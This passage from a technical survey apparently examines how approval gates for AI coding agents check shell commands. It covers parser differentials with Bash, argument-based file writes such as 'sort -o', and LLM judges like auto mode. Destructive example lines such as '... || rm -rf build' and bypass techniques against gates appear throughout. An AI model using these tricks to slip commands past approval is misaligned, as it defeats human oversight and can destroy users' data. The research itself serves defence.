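If `./check` fails, the alias `x` expands to nothing and the second line is a loop. If it succeeds, the line begins with `ls for`, and the shell reports a syntax error when it reaches `do`. To parse the second line in advance, a checker would have to determine whether `./check` will succeed, which no program can do for every possible `./check`. Parsing unrestricted shell scripts is therefore undecidable. It is decidable if scripts define aliases only outside conditionals and loops.

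In practice, constructs like these are rare. Jeannerod and colleagues examined 31,521 scripts that install and remove software on Debian, a Linux distribution. Only two used `alias`, and only 30 used `eval`, which assembles text and runs it as a command. A gate can require approval whenever `eval` appears. Bash also ignores aliases by default in commands it receives through `-c`, though some other shells don't. Experienced maintainers wrote these scripts, which may not resemble what agents write, but the counts suggest that undecidability matters mainly when an attacker chooses the commands.

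Even the ordinary rules of shell syntax make a parser complicated. In 2017, the parser in dash, a small shell, was 1,569 lines of hand-written C. Bash had a formal grammar plus about 5,000 more lines to handle the peculiarities of shell syntax. Jeannerod and colleagues copied the grammar rules from the POSIX standard into their own parser and needed only about 250 extra lines, though they used a more concise language and didn't support Bash's extensions. *Morbig*, the later paper on this parser, argues that parsing code like that in existing shells is hard to trust because readers can't easily relate it to the standard.

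### Differences between shells

A checker also needs to know which shell will receive the text. Seven of the eight agents in Li's study start either `/bin/bash` or `/bin/sh`, and the eighth sends the line to the shell in its terminal. On Debian and Ubuntu, `/bin/sh` is normally dash. Consider this line:

```
[[ 2.0 > 1.9 ]] && echo newer
```

In Bash, `[[` begins a test and `>` compares two pieces of text, so the line prints `newer`. Dash doesn't have this kind of test, so it treats `[[` as the name of a program and `>` as a redirection. It creates or empties a file called `1.9`, then reports that it can't find the program. A checker built for Bash would correctly find no file access in the line, but that finding would be wrong if dash ran it.

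The POSIX standard leaves some of these choices open. Greenberg and Blatt (2019), in *Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell*, counted 70 relevant uses of "unspecified", for valid input whose result the standard doesn't fix, and 17 of "undefined", for invalid input. Each shell also adds its own variants and extensions, as *ShellFuzzer* (2024) notes.

Shells also differ on points that the POSIX standard settles. Greenberg and Blatt ran 418 tests from the official POSIX test suite on several shells. Bash failed 4, dash 20, yash 22, ksh 23 and mksh 35. Zsh and a newer shell called OSH couldn't run the suite. The versions tested came from a Linux release of the time, and developers have had years to fix them since. The tests cover shell behavior in general, so a failure doesn't necessarily involve parsing.

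A difference in how the checker and the shell read the text is dangerous when it changes the gate's list of commands, or the words or redirections of a command on that list. Some differences only affect which of the listed commands run. For example, if a loop calls a function that contains `break`, zsh and an old version of Bash supplied with macOS leave the loop, while most shells keep going. A gate that lists the commands in every branch, whether or not they run, has the same list either way.

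### Comparing checkers with Bash

Li's testing framework, ParseGap, looks for dangerous differences by giving the same input to a checker and to Bash. Li first defines the usual kind of gate, *G*. Given a command string *s*, it works like this:

```
commands found:   parse_G(s)
decision:         δ_G(s) = rules_G(parse_G(s)), one of allow, ask or deny
after an allow:   the gate passes s to a shell
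```

The rules apply to `parse_G(s)`, but the shell receives `s`. The definition also covers the shell's sandbox settings, which the gate may select.

The other two definitions concern what happens when Bash runs the string. Let σ be the starting state, made up of the workspace, the files outside it and the environment variables. `Eff(s, σ)` is the set of effects that Li observes when Bash runs *s* in that state without a sandbox. It includes every program that starts, with its arguments, and every lasting change to the monitored files.

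```
s is active:      Eff(s, σ) contains at least one effect that the policy prohibits
G violates the
policy on s:      s is active and δ_G(s) = allow
```

A violation involves a parser differential if the gate and Bash differ on where a command ends or which words it contains, and the gate allows the line because of that difference. Other violations occur even though both parse the line into the same commands, for instance when a permitted program does harm through its arguments.

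The crude checker always parses the `login#2` line differently from the shell. But if `git status` and `tee` succeed and `pipefail` is off, the shell never starts `rm`. The line then isn't active under the example policy, so allowing it isn't a violation. If `git status` fails, the shell does start `rm`, and allowing the line is a violation.

ParseGap tests a product by calling its unmodified checker on an input and separately running that input in Bash 5.2. Bash runs in a container with no network connection, and ParseGap resets the container's workspace before every run. A tracing tool records each program that starts, and ParseGap compares the files in the workspace, and in two locations outside it, before and after the run.

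Li gave every product the same policy, as closely as its rule language allowed. The main policy was read-only and prohibited any lasting file change and any program not on the allowed list. The inputs included 34 examples from published advisories, 420 combinations of shell syntax and 3,000 automatically varied commands. When Li ran them, 33 of the advisory examples, 405 of the syntax combinations and 2,685 of the varied commands were active.

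Li traced the violations in the whole study to 17 root causes, counting variants that passed through the same faulty decision as one cause. Seven of the 17 were parser differentials. One defect in a third-party parsing library hid a second command from the checkers of two agents. Most of the other ten causes arose even though the gate had found the right commands, or came from permissive default settings.

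The eight checkers allowed between 1.5% and 55.8% of the 405 active combinations of shell syntax. Five allowed 4% or less, while the other three allowed at least 44%. These figures reflect more than parsing, because some checkers read a redirection correctly but had no rule against it, and in one case a later step overrode a warning that the checker had correctly raised.

The problem also occurs outside laboratory tests. Li counted 171 public security advisories from July 2025 to October 2026 about ways to bypass shell approval. Of these, 58 were spread across ten mainstream coding agents, and 113 were for a single open-source agent.

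### What observed effects can and cannot settle

A more common way to test a checker is to write down the correct verdict for each input and count the mismatches. But the person writing the verdicts can also misread the shell text, and if they make the same mistake as the checker, the test passes. Someone who believed that `#` always starts a comment would mark the `login#2` line as allowed and find nothing wrong with the crude checker. Running the line in Bash avoids this problem because the result doesn't depend on anyone's understanding of the syntax.

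Li can also use observed effects to compare very different checkers. One may produce a tree and another a list of words, but Li needs only each checker's final decision and a record of what Bash did.

However, the method can miss differentials. A hidden command leaves no trace if it doesn't run in the test container. Li focused on changes to files and on which programs start, not on secrets that a permitted program might read, so a differential that let an agent read a private file with `cat` could go uncounted. The method also compares every file in the workspace but checks only two locations outside it.

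The results also cover only one version of Bash on Linux and particular versions of eight products. Li left out closed-source tools whose terms prohibit automated testing. Most importantly, the inputs were attempts to break the policy, so the percentages don't measure how often an agent doing routine work would write a line that its gate misreads. Still, the seven differentials show that the first premise of segment-by-segment checking, that the list contains every command that can run, fails in products people use.

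### A better parser

Developers can fix each difference between the checker's parsing and the shell's as they find it. A shared parsing library helps because one fix can reach every product that uses it, though a defect can also affect them all. Jeannerod and colleagues' careful parser accepted 31,484 of the 31,521 Debian scripts, or 99.9%.

A parser can accept a script and still misread it, as Jeannerod and colleagues acknowledge. The crude checker, for example, accepts the `login#2` line without error. They suggest, among other remedies, running the parser's output through an interpreter and comparing the results with those of an existing shell. Like Li's method, this can find disagreements but can't show that none remain.

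A mathematical proof that two parsers agree would be better, but a program cannot always find one. A context-free grammar is a set of rules that can describe nested structures such as matching parentheses. Momot and colleagues point out that no general procedure can decide whether two such grammars accept exactly the same texts. A procedure does exist for a simpler class, the deterministic context-free languages, which a parser can read from left to right with a single stack and never more than one possible next step.

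This result doesn't rule out proving that two particular parsers accept the same texts. But even then, the parsers could assign different structures to those texts. For example, a parser that used C's precedence rule would accept `true || echo foo && echo bar`, as the shell does, but group it differently.

Fixing disagreements between the checker's parser and the shell is still worthwhile, because each fix lets a deny rule catch something it used to miss. But an attacker needs only one remaining disagreement to get past an allow rule, so a parser that is right about 99.9% of ordinary scripts could still be easy to bypass.

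### The shell's own parser

The gate could instead use the same parsing code as the shell. Android's developers eventually adopted this kind of remedy, running the package's data through the same parser on both sides. Sharing a parser would remove most disagreements between the gate and the shell about quotation marks, line breaks and here-documents, including those caused by bugs in the shell, since the gate would have the same bugs.

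Shell developers didn't write their parsers for use in safety checkers. Greenberg and Blatt built Smoosh, a formal model of the shell, around dash's parser and ran into several drawbacks. The parser includes code for displaying prompts, and it mishandles multibyte characters. It is also written in C, so a malformed line might corrupt the checker's memory. In one set of tests they ran, Smoosh's only failure came from dash's parser.

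The gate's parser also has to match the shell that will run the line. Dash's parser would misread the `[[` example if Bash were going to run it, and a recent Bash parser might misread a line that an older Bash will run. Settings and aliases have to match too. If the first line of a script changes them, the parser would have to apply the change before reading the second line. A gate that starts the shell itself can control much of this by fixing the version and settings and not loading the user's aliases.

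### A small subset of the language

Momot and colleagues recommend simplifying the language until checking it is easy. A gate can't change what the shell accepts, but it can choose which lines to approve automatically. It might approve only lines of this form:

```
word:      one or more of A–Z a–z 0–9 _ - . /
command:   words separated by spaces
line:      commands joined by &&, ||, ; or |
```

The original example line fits, and the gate would find the same four commands in it as Bash or dash would. Without quotation marks, nothing can be nested, so a single regular expression can recognize every valid line. Momot and colleagues call languages this simple the most preferable kind. Words with a special meaning, such as `for`, matter only where a command could begin. They aren't on the allow list, so the gate asks for approval.

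The `login#2` line contains `#`, which isn't in the gate's listed syntax, so the gate prompts for approval. It doesn't have to interpret `#` in that position, which is the advantage Joshi pointed out in gates that list only the syntax they can interpret.

The gate still depends on a few facts about the shell, such as whether a user has defined an alias or function called `git`. The gate and the shell should parse any line in the subset the same way, but the shell still parses the text a second time unless the gate starts the approved programs itself.

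This approach causes more false alarms. With the rules above, `git commit -m "fix login"` would always need approval because of its quotation marks. Accepting a larger subset of the syntax reduces the number of prompts but gives the developer more syntax to handle correctly. Li's gate, ShellPlan, accepts variables, wildcards and nested commands. It stopped 12 of the 161 harmless commands in Li's test (7.5%), compared with 37 for Codex, which accepts only plain words. Both totals include some stops unrelated to syntax.

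Agents can often avoid the unsupported syntax. Li gave ten models four tasks each, with prompts that deliberately asked for shell features outside ShellPlan's subset, such as `~` for the home directory. Nobody was available to approve commands. ShellPlan stopped the first such command in all 40 runs, but the agents still completed 25 of the tasks by rewriting the command or using another tool. Without a gate, they completed all 40.

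The six frontier models completed 20 of 24 tasks under ShellPlan, while the four smaller models completed only 5 of 16. A strict subset may therefore require little more than an extra attempt from a capable agent. With a weaker agent, a person would have to approve more commands or accept that more tasks will fail.

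## What a correctly identified command will do

A gate can find every command in a line, agree with the shell about every word, and still misjudge what the line will do. `sort` normally prints the lines of a file in order and changes nothing, so a user might reasonably allow it as a read-only program. But consider these two commands:

```
sort names.txt
sort -o names.txt names.txt
```

The first command prints the sorted names. The second command uses the documented option `-o`, which sets an output file, so `sort` replaces `names.txt` with the sorted version. A rule that permits `sort` permits both.

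Segment-by-segment checking assumes that a command's text fixes its effect. A rule about the program's name ignores most of that text, and part of what determines the effect isn't in the text at all. Each command in this table starts with a program that usually only reads:

| What changes the effect | Example | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| An option | `sort -o names.txt names.txt` | replaces the file |
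| An operand (an argument that isn't an option) | `uniq names.txt short.txt` | writes the second file |
| A redirection | `git log > log.txt` | the shell writes the file |
| An environment variable | `GIT_TRACE=/tmp/trace git status` | `git` adds a log of its work to the file |
| A configuration file | `git status` | `git` may run a program that the repository's settings name |

In the example line, `tee test.log` is supposed to write a file. The example policy doesn't limit which files `tee` may write, so it also permits `tee package.json`, which would overwrite the file that defines the project's tests. A gate that allows this has applied the policy correctly, but the rule is too broad, probably because whoever wrote it was thinking of log files.

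Even `tee test.log` can write outside the project, because if `test.log` is a symbolic link, `tee` overwrites the file it points to. Jing's gate therefore follows links before it checks a path, and Jing's tests required it to give different verdicts on the same text when the effect differed. The gate stopped all 25 scripts that had forbidden effects when run without it. It blocked no harmless scripts, but the test included only eight.

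If a gate checks files, its verdicts depend on which files are present. Jing put 50 defects into the gate, one at a time, to see whether the tests would detect them. The tests detected 46, but they detected 47 after Jing deleted one file from the test directory.

### Fifty-five cases built from permitted tools

Li tested the effects of arguments separately from parsing. The 55 cases used only inspection programs that the read-only policy permitted and relied on features described in their manuals. All 55 broke the policy when Li ran them in Bash, either by writing a file or, in 18 cases, by starting another program.

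All eight checkers allowed some of them. One allowed 9, another 20, and the other six between 39 and 47. The causes were output-file arguments, options that run other programs, and environment variables set at the start of the command. Four checkers also had no guard against output redirections.

An early prototype of Li's own gate, ShellPlan, had no rules for arguments and allowed 32 of the 55. Better parsing couldn't have stopped those 32, because the gate already split them into the same commands and words as Bash did. Parsing identifies `-o` as an argument of `sort`, but the gate needs a separate rule specifying that `-o` writes a file. Once Li added such rules, ShellPlan allowed none of the 55. Its rules covered four of the harmless commands in the same test, and it still allowed all four.

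The recordings of agents at work better show how often such commands come up in routine use. Under the same read-only policy, three of the checkers each allowed about 350 of the recorded commands, nine of which changed a file. Five of these changes were side effects that Li had decided in advance to set aside, such as `git` refreshing its own index. The other four came from `sed -i`, which edits a file in place, and a deny rule for that form would have stopped them. Forbidding a few common forms may therefore be enough for an agent doing routine work, but an attacker can choose a less common one.

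### Forbidden arguments and permitted arguments

A gate can list the arguments it forbids or the arguments it permits. Forbidding just the output option of `sort` takes several patterns. Its long form is `--output`, which users can shorten to `--out` in GNU's version. Its short form, `-o`, can be combined with other options, as in `-no`, which also sorts numerically. Another option names a program that `sort` runs to compress its temporary files, so it needs a rule as well.

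One of the products in Li's study has 15 hand-written guards for individual programs and a check on file paths, but it allowed 20 of the 55 cases. Lists of forbidden programs, or denylists, have similar gaps. In *One Goal, Many Commands*, Chen and Lin (2026) tested 1,709 real denylists from GitHub against seven file operations. For each operation, between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists that aimed to block it missed at least one command that could perform it.

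A positive description lists what is permitted and leaves everything else for a person to approve. One for `sort` might look like this:

```
program:     sort
options:     -n, -r, -u, -k FIELD, -t CHARACTER
operands:    any number of files to read
variables:   language and time zone settings
otherwise:   ask
```

Anything new needs approval by default, as with a list of permitted syntax, so this description still works if a later version of `sort` adds another option that writes files.

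ShellPlan has descriptions like this for 20 common programs. It permits at most one operand for `uniq`, so the command can't name an output file. `sed` is harder because its argument is a small program that can write files or run commands. ShellPlan passes that program to `sed` in a restricted mode that rejects both, and keeps the restriction on when it runs the command.

The gate also has to interpret arguments the way the program does. Lamprou and colleagues point out that a program receives its arguments as plain strings and interprets them itself. In `uniq -f 1 names.txt`, the `1` is the value of `-f`, which makes `uniq` ignore the first field of each line. A gate that counted `1` as an operand would mistake `names.txt` for an output file and raise a false alarm. The opposite mistake, treating an output file as the value of an option that takes none, is worse. When Li compared ShellPlan's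 descriptions with the installed programs, the first round found nine disagreements about whether an option takes the next word as its value, and the final round found none in 1,213 options.

Wildcards can also change what a command does. If a directory contains a file called `--output=names.txt`, the shell includes that name when it expands `sort *`, and `sort` treats it as an option. ShellPlan's second check, which runs after expansion, can catch this.

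These descriptions take a lot of work to write. Lamprou and colleagues report that two experts spent more than 200 hours studying the documentation of 120 commands just to decide which types of argument their descriptions should distinguish. Their automatic generator, Caruca, described 99.7% of the options and arguments correctly. That may be good enough for a tool that speeds up scripts, but a single mistake about an output option can cause a false allow in a gate. Programs also differ between Linux and macOS, so one description may not fit both.

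Missing descriptions cause false alarms, as in the 68 read-only steps that ShellPlan stopped in Li's recordings because of `nl`.

Redirections are easier to describe because the shell handles them the same way for every program. Joshi compares two rules for a gate. The first rule requires approval for any redirection, which produces so many prompts that people learn to click yes. The second requires approval for all redirections except those that discard output or merge one stream into another, such as `2>&1`.

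### Settings and files outside the command

Checking arguments doesn't settle what `git status` will do, because its effect also depends on the repository. Joshi gives four conditions for treating it as read-only:

- No option points `git` at another directory or configuration.
- The line doesn't also change directory.
- The line doesn't first create the files that `git` uses to store a repository.
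- Neither the current directory nor any directory above it contains such files laid out as a bare repository (one without the usual `.git` directory), or a link to repository data that nobody has verified.

The text of the example line, `git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build`, satisfies the first three, but the gate has to inspect the disk to check the fourth.

ShellPlan reads the repository's settings before it starts `git`, and continues only if each is on a permitted list. The list leaves out settings that can name a program for `git` to run. Li tested 85 permitted settings with nine `git` commands each, and none of the 765 runs started an unexpected program.

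A command gate can't help if the agent's own software runs `git`. Li found that in one product, a routine `git` call at startup ran a program named in the repository's settings before the model had proposed any command.

`npm test` is harder still, because a description can permit `test` and forbid every other argument, but the project's files define what the tests do. Li therefore leaves `npm` out of ShellPlan's guarantees about which files a command can write. In the recordings, under a policy that also allowed `pytest`, a program that runs Python tests, 44 of the 398 commands ShellPlan allowed had effects outside the policy, and all 44 were test runs. Many of these effects may have been harmless, since `pytest` normally saves cache files, but the gate couldn't have determined that from the command's text.

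### Scoring how dangerous a command looks

CARE, the gate that Liu and colleagues built, scores how dangerous a command looks instead of comparing it with a user's list. It first puts the command into a standard form, without running any of it, by removing wrappers such as `bash -c` and undoing simple disguises. Then it gives the command four scores between 0 and 1:

- *Meaning* depends on the program and its options. `ls` scores 0, `curl` scores 0.40, and a program CARE doesn't recognize scores 0.35.
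- *Path* depends on which files the command uses and how. Reading an ordinary file in `/etc`, where system settings are kept, scores 0.10, and writing one scores 0.70.
- *Pattern* depends on whether the command matches any of 139 rules for known dangerous forms.
- *Structure* depends on how the line is put together. An ordinary pipe scores 0.05, and a pipe into a program such as `bash` or `python` scores 1.

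CARE combines them into a total:

```
score = 0.3 × meaning + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

below 0.15:             allow
from 0.15 up to 0.35:   warn
0.35 or more:           deny
```

In the last stage, CARE resolves warnings by denying the command if one kind of evidence is strong, such as a write to a protected file, and otherwise following a language model's verdict. For example, a command that used `rsync` to copy a build directory to another machine scored 0.40 for meaning and 0.75 for pattern, for a total of 0.345. The model classified it as safe, so CARE allowed it.

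On the test set of 549 commands, CARE caught 167 of the 220 dangerous commands (75.91%) and wrongly stopped 3 of the 329 safe ones (0.91%). The model decided only 23 cases. A static version without the model, which blocks every command that triggers a warning, caught the same 167 and wrongly stopped 6 safe commands, a difference small enough to be due to chance.

When dangerous commands are rare, even a low false alarm rate can mean that a check stops more safe commands than dangerous ones. Liu and colleagues calculate that if 1% of 10,000 commands were dangerous, CARE would stop about 76 dangerous commands and 90 safe ones, and miss 24 dangerous ones. When they lowered the warning threshold of the static version from 0.15 to 0.10, it caught more of the dangerous commands (96.82%) but also stopped 23.10% of the safe ones.

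### What the syntax layer added

Liu and colleagues also removed one layer at a time from the static version and measured the change in F1. With dangerous commands as the ones to catch, F1 is:

```
F1 = 2 × caught / (2 × caught + missed + false alarms)
```

Scores range from 0% for a gate that catches nothing to 100% for a perfect gate. The full static version scores 334 / (334 + 53 + 6), or 84.99%.

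| Layer removed | Dangerous commands caught, of 220 | False alarms, of 329 | Loss in F1, in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 167 | 6 | – |
| Syntax and structure | 161 | 6 | 1.79 |
| Patterns | 134 | 1 | 9.50 |
| Paths | 116 | 5 | 16.95 |
| Command meaning | 93 | 6 | 26.68 |

This is good evidence that a gate needs to know what programs do and which files they affect, but much weaker evidence that parsing matters little. The structure score can add at most 0.1 to the total, so it can never trigger a warning by itself. The other layers also partly overlap with it, because a rule can still catch a known dangerous pipeline by matching its text.

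The test set may also have had too few lines where parsing would make a difference. Liu and colleagues don't say how many of the 549 commands join several simple commands. By their approximate categories, only five of the dangerous ones download something and run it, where the connection between commands matters a great deal. A better test would put the same dangerous command first in a line, after `&&`, after a pipe and inside quotation marks, and compare how often each version caught it.

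### A language model as judge

A language model can also check every command instead of only the doubtful ones. Liu and colleagues tested this with Qwen3-Coder-30B, a fairly small model that received only the command and output one word. It caught 67.27% of the dangerous commands in the main test and stopped 11.25% of the safe ones, doing worse than CARE on both measures.

The model did better than CARE at spotting dangerous uses of ordinary programs. Liu and colleagues separately tested both on 69 commands from GTFOBins, a public catalogue of standard programs that people can use to get around security restrictions. Judging from the published scores, the model caught 61 of the 69 and CARE caught 41. But the model also stopped 16 of 69 safe commands, while CARE stopped 9. The model may have learned from manuals and examples what many unusual options do, while CARE depends on what its developers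 wrote into it.

Adding the same model to CARE as a final judge raised the number of attack commands that got through and ran successfully from 224 to 315 out of 600. The judge reviews only commands that CARE's static version would block, so it can release commands but can't block more. It released 92, and 91 of those ran. The same model had written the attacks, which may be why it approved them. A judge from a different model family might have released fewer.

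Li compared a newer model, deepseek-v4.1-flash, with ShellPlan and with a gate taken from one of the eight products. Ten models each attempted nine attack tasks and ten harmless ones, with nobody available to approve commands:

| Gate | Successful attacks, of 90 | Standard tasks completed, of 60 | Tasks with unusual syntax completed, of 40 | Median time spent in the gate per task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
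| None | 62 | 53 | 40 | – |
| Existing product's gate | 56 | 45 | 39 | 2.11 ms |
| Language model judge | 6 | 50 | 37 | 6.06 s |
| ShellPlan | 0 | 49 | 25 | 1.28 ms |

The judge stopped most of the attacks and interfered less than ShellPlan with unusual but harmless commands. On standard tasks, the two did about equally well. Li designed both ShellPlan and the tasks, and 90 attempts are too few to measure rare failures, but the judge's advantage on harmless commands is large. The judge adds about six seconds per task, which matters less if the alternative is waiting for a person.

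The model behind Claude Code's auto mode may be the most widely used judge of this kind. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, interactive sessions in recent versions start in auto mode unless a setting changes this. Anthropic instructs this model to consider an action's real effect and to treat a chain joined by `&&` as a single action. If an agent writes a script and then runs it, the model is supposed to judge what the script does.

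The model also looks for evidence that the user authorized the action, which can't be checked with a list of commands. It could allow `rm -rf build` in the example line if the user had asked the agent to delete failed builds. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. A request to "clean up the PR", for example, doesn't authorize overwriting the history of a shared repository.

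In Anthropic's experiment with paid testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, while the testers blocked 13.6%. Those commands were clearly dangerous, so they were probably easier to judge than the real cases in which an agent had gone too far. Auto mode missed 17% of those real cases. Separately, the safety company Apollo Research wrote attacks aimed at auto mode. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after Anthropic gave the model more information, including the state of the repository and whether it was public. This suggests that the model missed some of the earlier attacks because it lacked facts that weren't in the command.

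When Anthropic described the design, the model saw the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tools' output. Leaving out the output protects the model from instructions planted in files, but it also means the model probably couldn't read the tests that `npm test` would run unless the agent had written them in the same session.

In auto mode, Anthropic sets aside allow rules broad enough to run any code, but other allow rules still apply before the command reaches the model. If one of these narrower rules covers more than the user realized, auto mode doesn't correct it. Deny rules and explicit ask rules also still apply, so someone who wants the example policy's prompt for `rm` can write an ask rule for it.

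A language model may identify the purpose of a line more accurately than any list can, but its verdict still applies to text that the shell will parse separately. A model could misread the `#` in the `login#2` line just as the crude checker did, miss the deletion, and allow it. If the model gives only a one-word answer, there is also no list of commands and arguments to compare with the ones the shell starts.

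## Running exactly what was approved

Most command gates judge their own version of a command line and then send the original text to a shell, which works out for itself what to start. To make the verdict apply to what runs, the computer has to execute the same object that the gate approved. For a gate *G* and a command string *s*, the difference looks small:

```
usual gate:   judge parse_G(s), then give s to a shell
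required:     p = parse_G(s), judge p, then run p
```

If the crude checker that cut the `login#2` line short at its `#` ran its own version of the line, it would start only `git status` and `npm test -- --grep login`. The misreading would still give the agent the wrong tests, but `rm -rf build` would not run.

### Changes between the check and the use

Since the 1970s, security designers have used a principle called complete mediation, which requires a system to check every access to every protected object. Under this principle, designers should also be suspicious of saving the results of checks, because saved results must be updated when permissions change.

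An approval is also a saved verdict. A person may take several minutes to answer a prompt, and meanwhile the agent or an attacker could replace a file that the command uses. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. A course at the University of Texas at Austin has students consider an automated tool that is about to publish grades for 120 people, where one score changes after someone has approved the action. The course teaches that an approval covers one exact action, including its content and targets, and lapses if any of that changes or too much time passes.

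Researchers have paid little attention to the problem in AI agents. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a survey, found only two papers on it. One of them, *Mind the Gap* (2025), covers agents in general and uses a benchmark of 66 tasks. Its countermeasures include rewriting the user's request so that the agent confirms the current state immediately before acting, monitoring the state for changes, and fusing tools. Together they cut the rate of such flaws in the agents' runs from 12% to 8%.

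A command gate can do better because it controls the launch. OpenClaw ties an approved command to its exact arguments, working directory and environment variables. It also records which file each program name refers to and checks this again just before launch. If another `git` has appeared in a directory earlier in `PATH`, OpenClaw refuses to run the command. For program files that someone could modify, it also compares a hash of the file's contents.

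The effect of `python3 report.py` depends on what is in `report.py`, so OpenClaw tries to record the script's contents as well. If it can't identify exactly one such file, it refuses to run the command on the basis of an approval. This happens with `npm test`, because `npm` looks up the actual test command in the project's files. The user then has to trust the program in advance or run it in a sandbox.

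Jing (2026), in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, measured the effect of these checks using a gate on Windows. The earliest version compared only a fingerprint of the stated action, so an attacker could get a harmless file approved, swap its contents and have the altered file run. With an added check of the file's bytes immediately before running it, the gate blocked 28 of 31 attacks of this general kind, up from 19. Making each approval valid for one use raised the share of blocked reuse attempts from 77.8% to 100%.

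A check just before launch still leaves a short gap, because a file can change after the last comparison and before the operating system opens it. A gate can close most of this gap by opening the file first, checking the opened file, and then using that same open file. Replacing the path with a link to another file then has no effect, although another program could still edit the file's contents.

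### What a program receives when no shell is involved

A gate can also leave the shell out. On Linux, a process starts a program through a request to the operating system called `execve`. According to the Linux Programmer's Manual's *execve(2)*, the request contains the path of the program file, a list of arguments and a list of environment variables. Each argument is a separate string. Suppose a gate used `execve` to start `git` with this argument list:

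```
["git", "status", "&&", "rm", "-rf", "build"]
```

`git` would start with five arguments after its own name, including `&&`. It would probably report an error, and `rm` would never start. Only a shell treats `&&` as an operator, and no shell reads this list. Semicolons, quotation marks, wildcards and `$(...)` are also ordinary characters here.

Direct dispatch means starting the approved program from its checked argument list in this way. It gains nothing if the program is itself a shell. For example, `["bash", "-lc", "git status && npm test"]`, from the Codex documentation, is an argument list, but Bash parses its third string as commands. If the program file is a script whose first line names an interpreter, Linux starts that interpreter and passes it the script's path.

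`execve` also starts only one program. It doesn't connect pipes or check whether an earlier command failed before running `rm`, so a gate that uses direct dispatch has to do both itself or accept only single commands.

### How ShellPlan turns a line into a plan

ShellPlan, Li's gate, does the work itself. It compiles the command string once into a data structure called a plan, and uses only the plan from then on. A plan *P* has this grammar:

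```
P is one of:   c
               P ; P
               P && P
               P || P
               P | P

c is a simple command:   ⟨ A, w0 w1 ... wn, R ⟩

A           assignments in front of the command
w0          the program's name, as literal text
w1 ... wn   arguments, built from literal text, variables,
            wildcards and nested plans $(P)
R           redirections, in the order written
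```

A nested plan is always smaller than the plan around it, so the checks eventually reach the innermost command. The grammar has no loops, functions or background commands. If a line uses one of these or another unsupported feature, such as `cd`, ShellPlan asks for approval before starting anything. It also asks if a variable supplies the program's name, as in `$tool build`.

ShellPlan next checks every command in the plan, including those that may never run. The plan passes if each command meets these conditions:

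- The policy permits the program, and the program isn't an interpreter such as `bash` or `python`.
- The arguments fit ShellPlan's description of the program, if it has one.
- Any assignments in front of the command set only permitted variables, such as the language or time zone.
- Each redirection leads to a permitted place.
- If the command runs alongside `git` in a pipeline, it obeys the rule that keeps other stages from changing the repository's settings.

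ShellPlan then runs the plan, following the operators as Bash would. It expands the words of a command only when it reaches that command. A variable may contain an option that the earlier check couldn't detect, so ShellPlan compares the actual arguments with the description and the user's deny rules. It also confirms that the program file is outside the workspace, the project directory where the agent works, so that a file named `grep` planted there by an attacker can't replace the real program.

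ShellPlan stops the run at some expansions. For example, if the variable `pattern` contains `*.txt`, Bash replaces an unquoted `$pattern` with `*.txt` and then with the names of matching files. ShellPlan halts instead of making the second replacement.

Under a read-only policy, ShellPlan allows output redirections only to `/dev/null`, which discards whatever it receives. If the policy permits writing in the workspace, ShellPlan opens a file such as `logs/test.log` in stages:

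1. It resolves the path again and confirms that it still leads to the approved location.
2. Starting from the top of the workspace, it opens each directory in the path, refusing symbolic links and directories that hold a repository's internal data.
3. It opens the file without emptying it, and refuses anything other than a regular file.
4. It refuses a file that has a second name elsewhere on the disk, because that name could be outside the workspace.
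5. Only then does it empty the file and connect it to the command.

ShellPlan empties a file last, so a file it refuses keeps its contents. Li tested ShellPlan with 1,000 attempted writes while another program kept swapping the target's directory for a link to a place outside the workspace. No write landed outside the workspace, but only 83 succeeded, and 741 attempts ended in errors that ShellPlan's code didn't handle.

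ShellPlan finally starts the program by direct dispatch. It handles plain `echo` and `pwd` commands itself.

### The example line as a plan

ShellPlan compiles the example line, `git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build`, into a plan with this structure:

```
( ⟨git status⟩ && ( ⟨npm test⟩ | ⟨tee test.log⟩ ) ) || ⟨rm -rf build⟩
```

Under the example policy, ShellPlan requests approval before starting any command, including `git status`, because `rm` isn't on the allow list. If a person approves, the gate has to run this stored plan, because sending the text to a shell would bring back the second parse. Li's main comparison with live agents had nobody available to approve commands, so it didn't test this step.

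Suppose the agent leaves out the deletion and proposes `git status && npm test | tee test.log`, which the policy permits. ShellPlan inspects the repository's settings, starts `git` with the argument list `["git", "status"]`, and waits for it to finish. If `git` returns 0, ShellPlan creates a pipe and starts two programs, with the argument lists `["npm", "test"]` and `["tee", "test.log"]`. None of the three programs receives `&&` or `|`.

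Two things are still outside ShellPlan's control. `npm` normally starts its own shell to run the project's test command, and ShellPlan doesn't check that command. `tee` opens `test.log` itself, so the five stages for opening a file don't apply. They would apply to `npm test > test.log` under a policy that permits writing in the workspace.

### What the theorems guarantee

Li proved two theorems about a formal model of ShellPlan.

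The single-interpretation theorem covers both rejected and admitted lines. If a line can't be compiled or its plan fails the checks, ShellPlan starts none of the line's commands and opens none of its redirection targets. If ShellPlan admits the line, every program it starts directly is either a command from the plan whose expanded arguments have passed the checks, or one of a few fixed read-only probes, such as those that read `git` settings. ShellPlan never passes any part of the line to a shell. The proof is by induction on the height of the plan, so it covers commands nested to any depth.

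The effect-containment theorem applies only if ShellPlan has a description of every program in the plan. The files written can then only be permitted redirection targets, temporary files that `sort` creates, or the index that `git` refreshes. The theorem limits which programs can start in a similar way. It depends on two assumptions:

- *Everything outside the workspace is trustworthy.* This includes the installed programs, the user's configuration and the inherited environment variables. The attacker controls only the files in the workspace and the text that the agent reads. The theorem makes an exception for helper programs that the trusted configuration starts.
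- *Each program behaves as described when it receives permitted arguments.* Li's tests of this used the versions installed in one container, and another version of `sort` or `git` might behave differently.

Effect containment doesn't cover `git status && npm test | tee test.log`, because `npm` runs code from the project and ShellPlan has no description of `tee`. Neither theorem rules out leaks, so a permitted `cat` could print a private file from outside the workspace. Li left such leaks out of the study, along with attempts to exhaust the computer's resources. The theorems also don't prove that running a plan gives the same result as running the original text in Bash.

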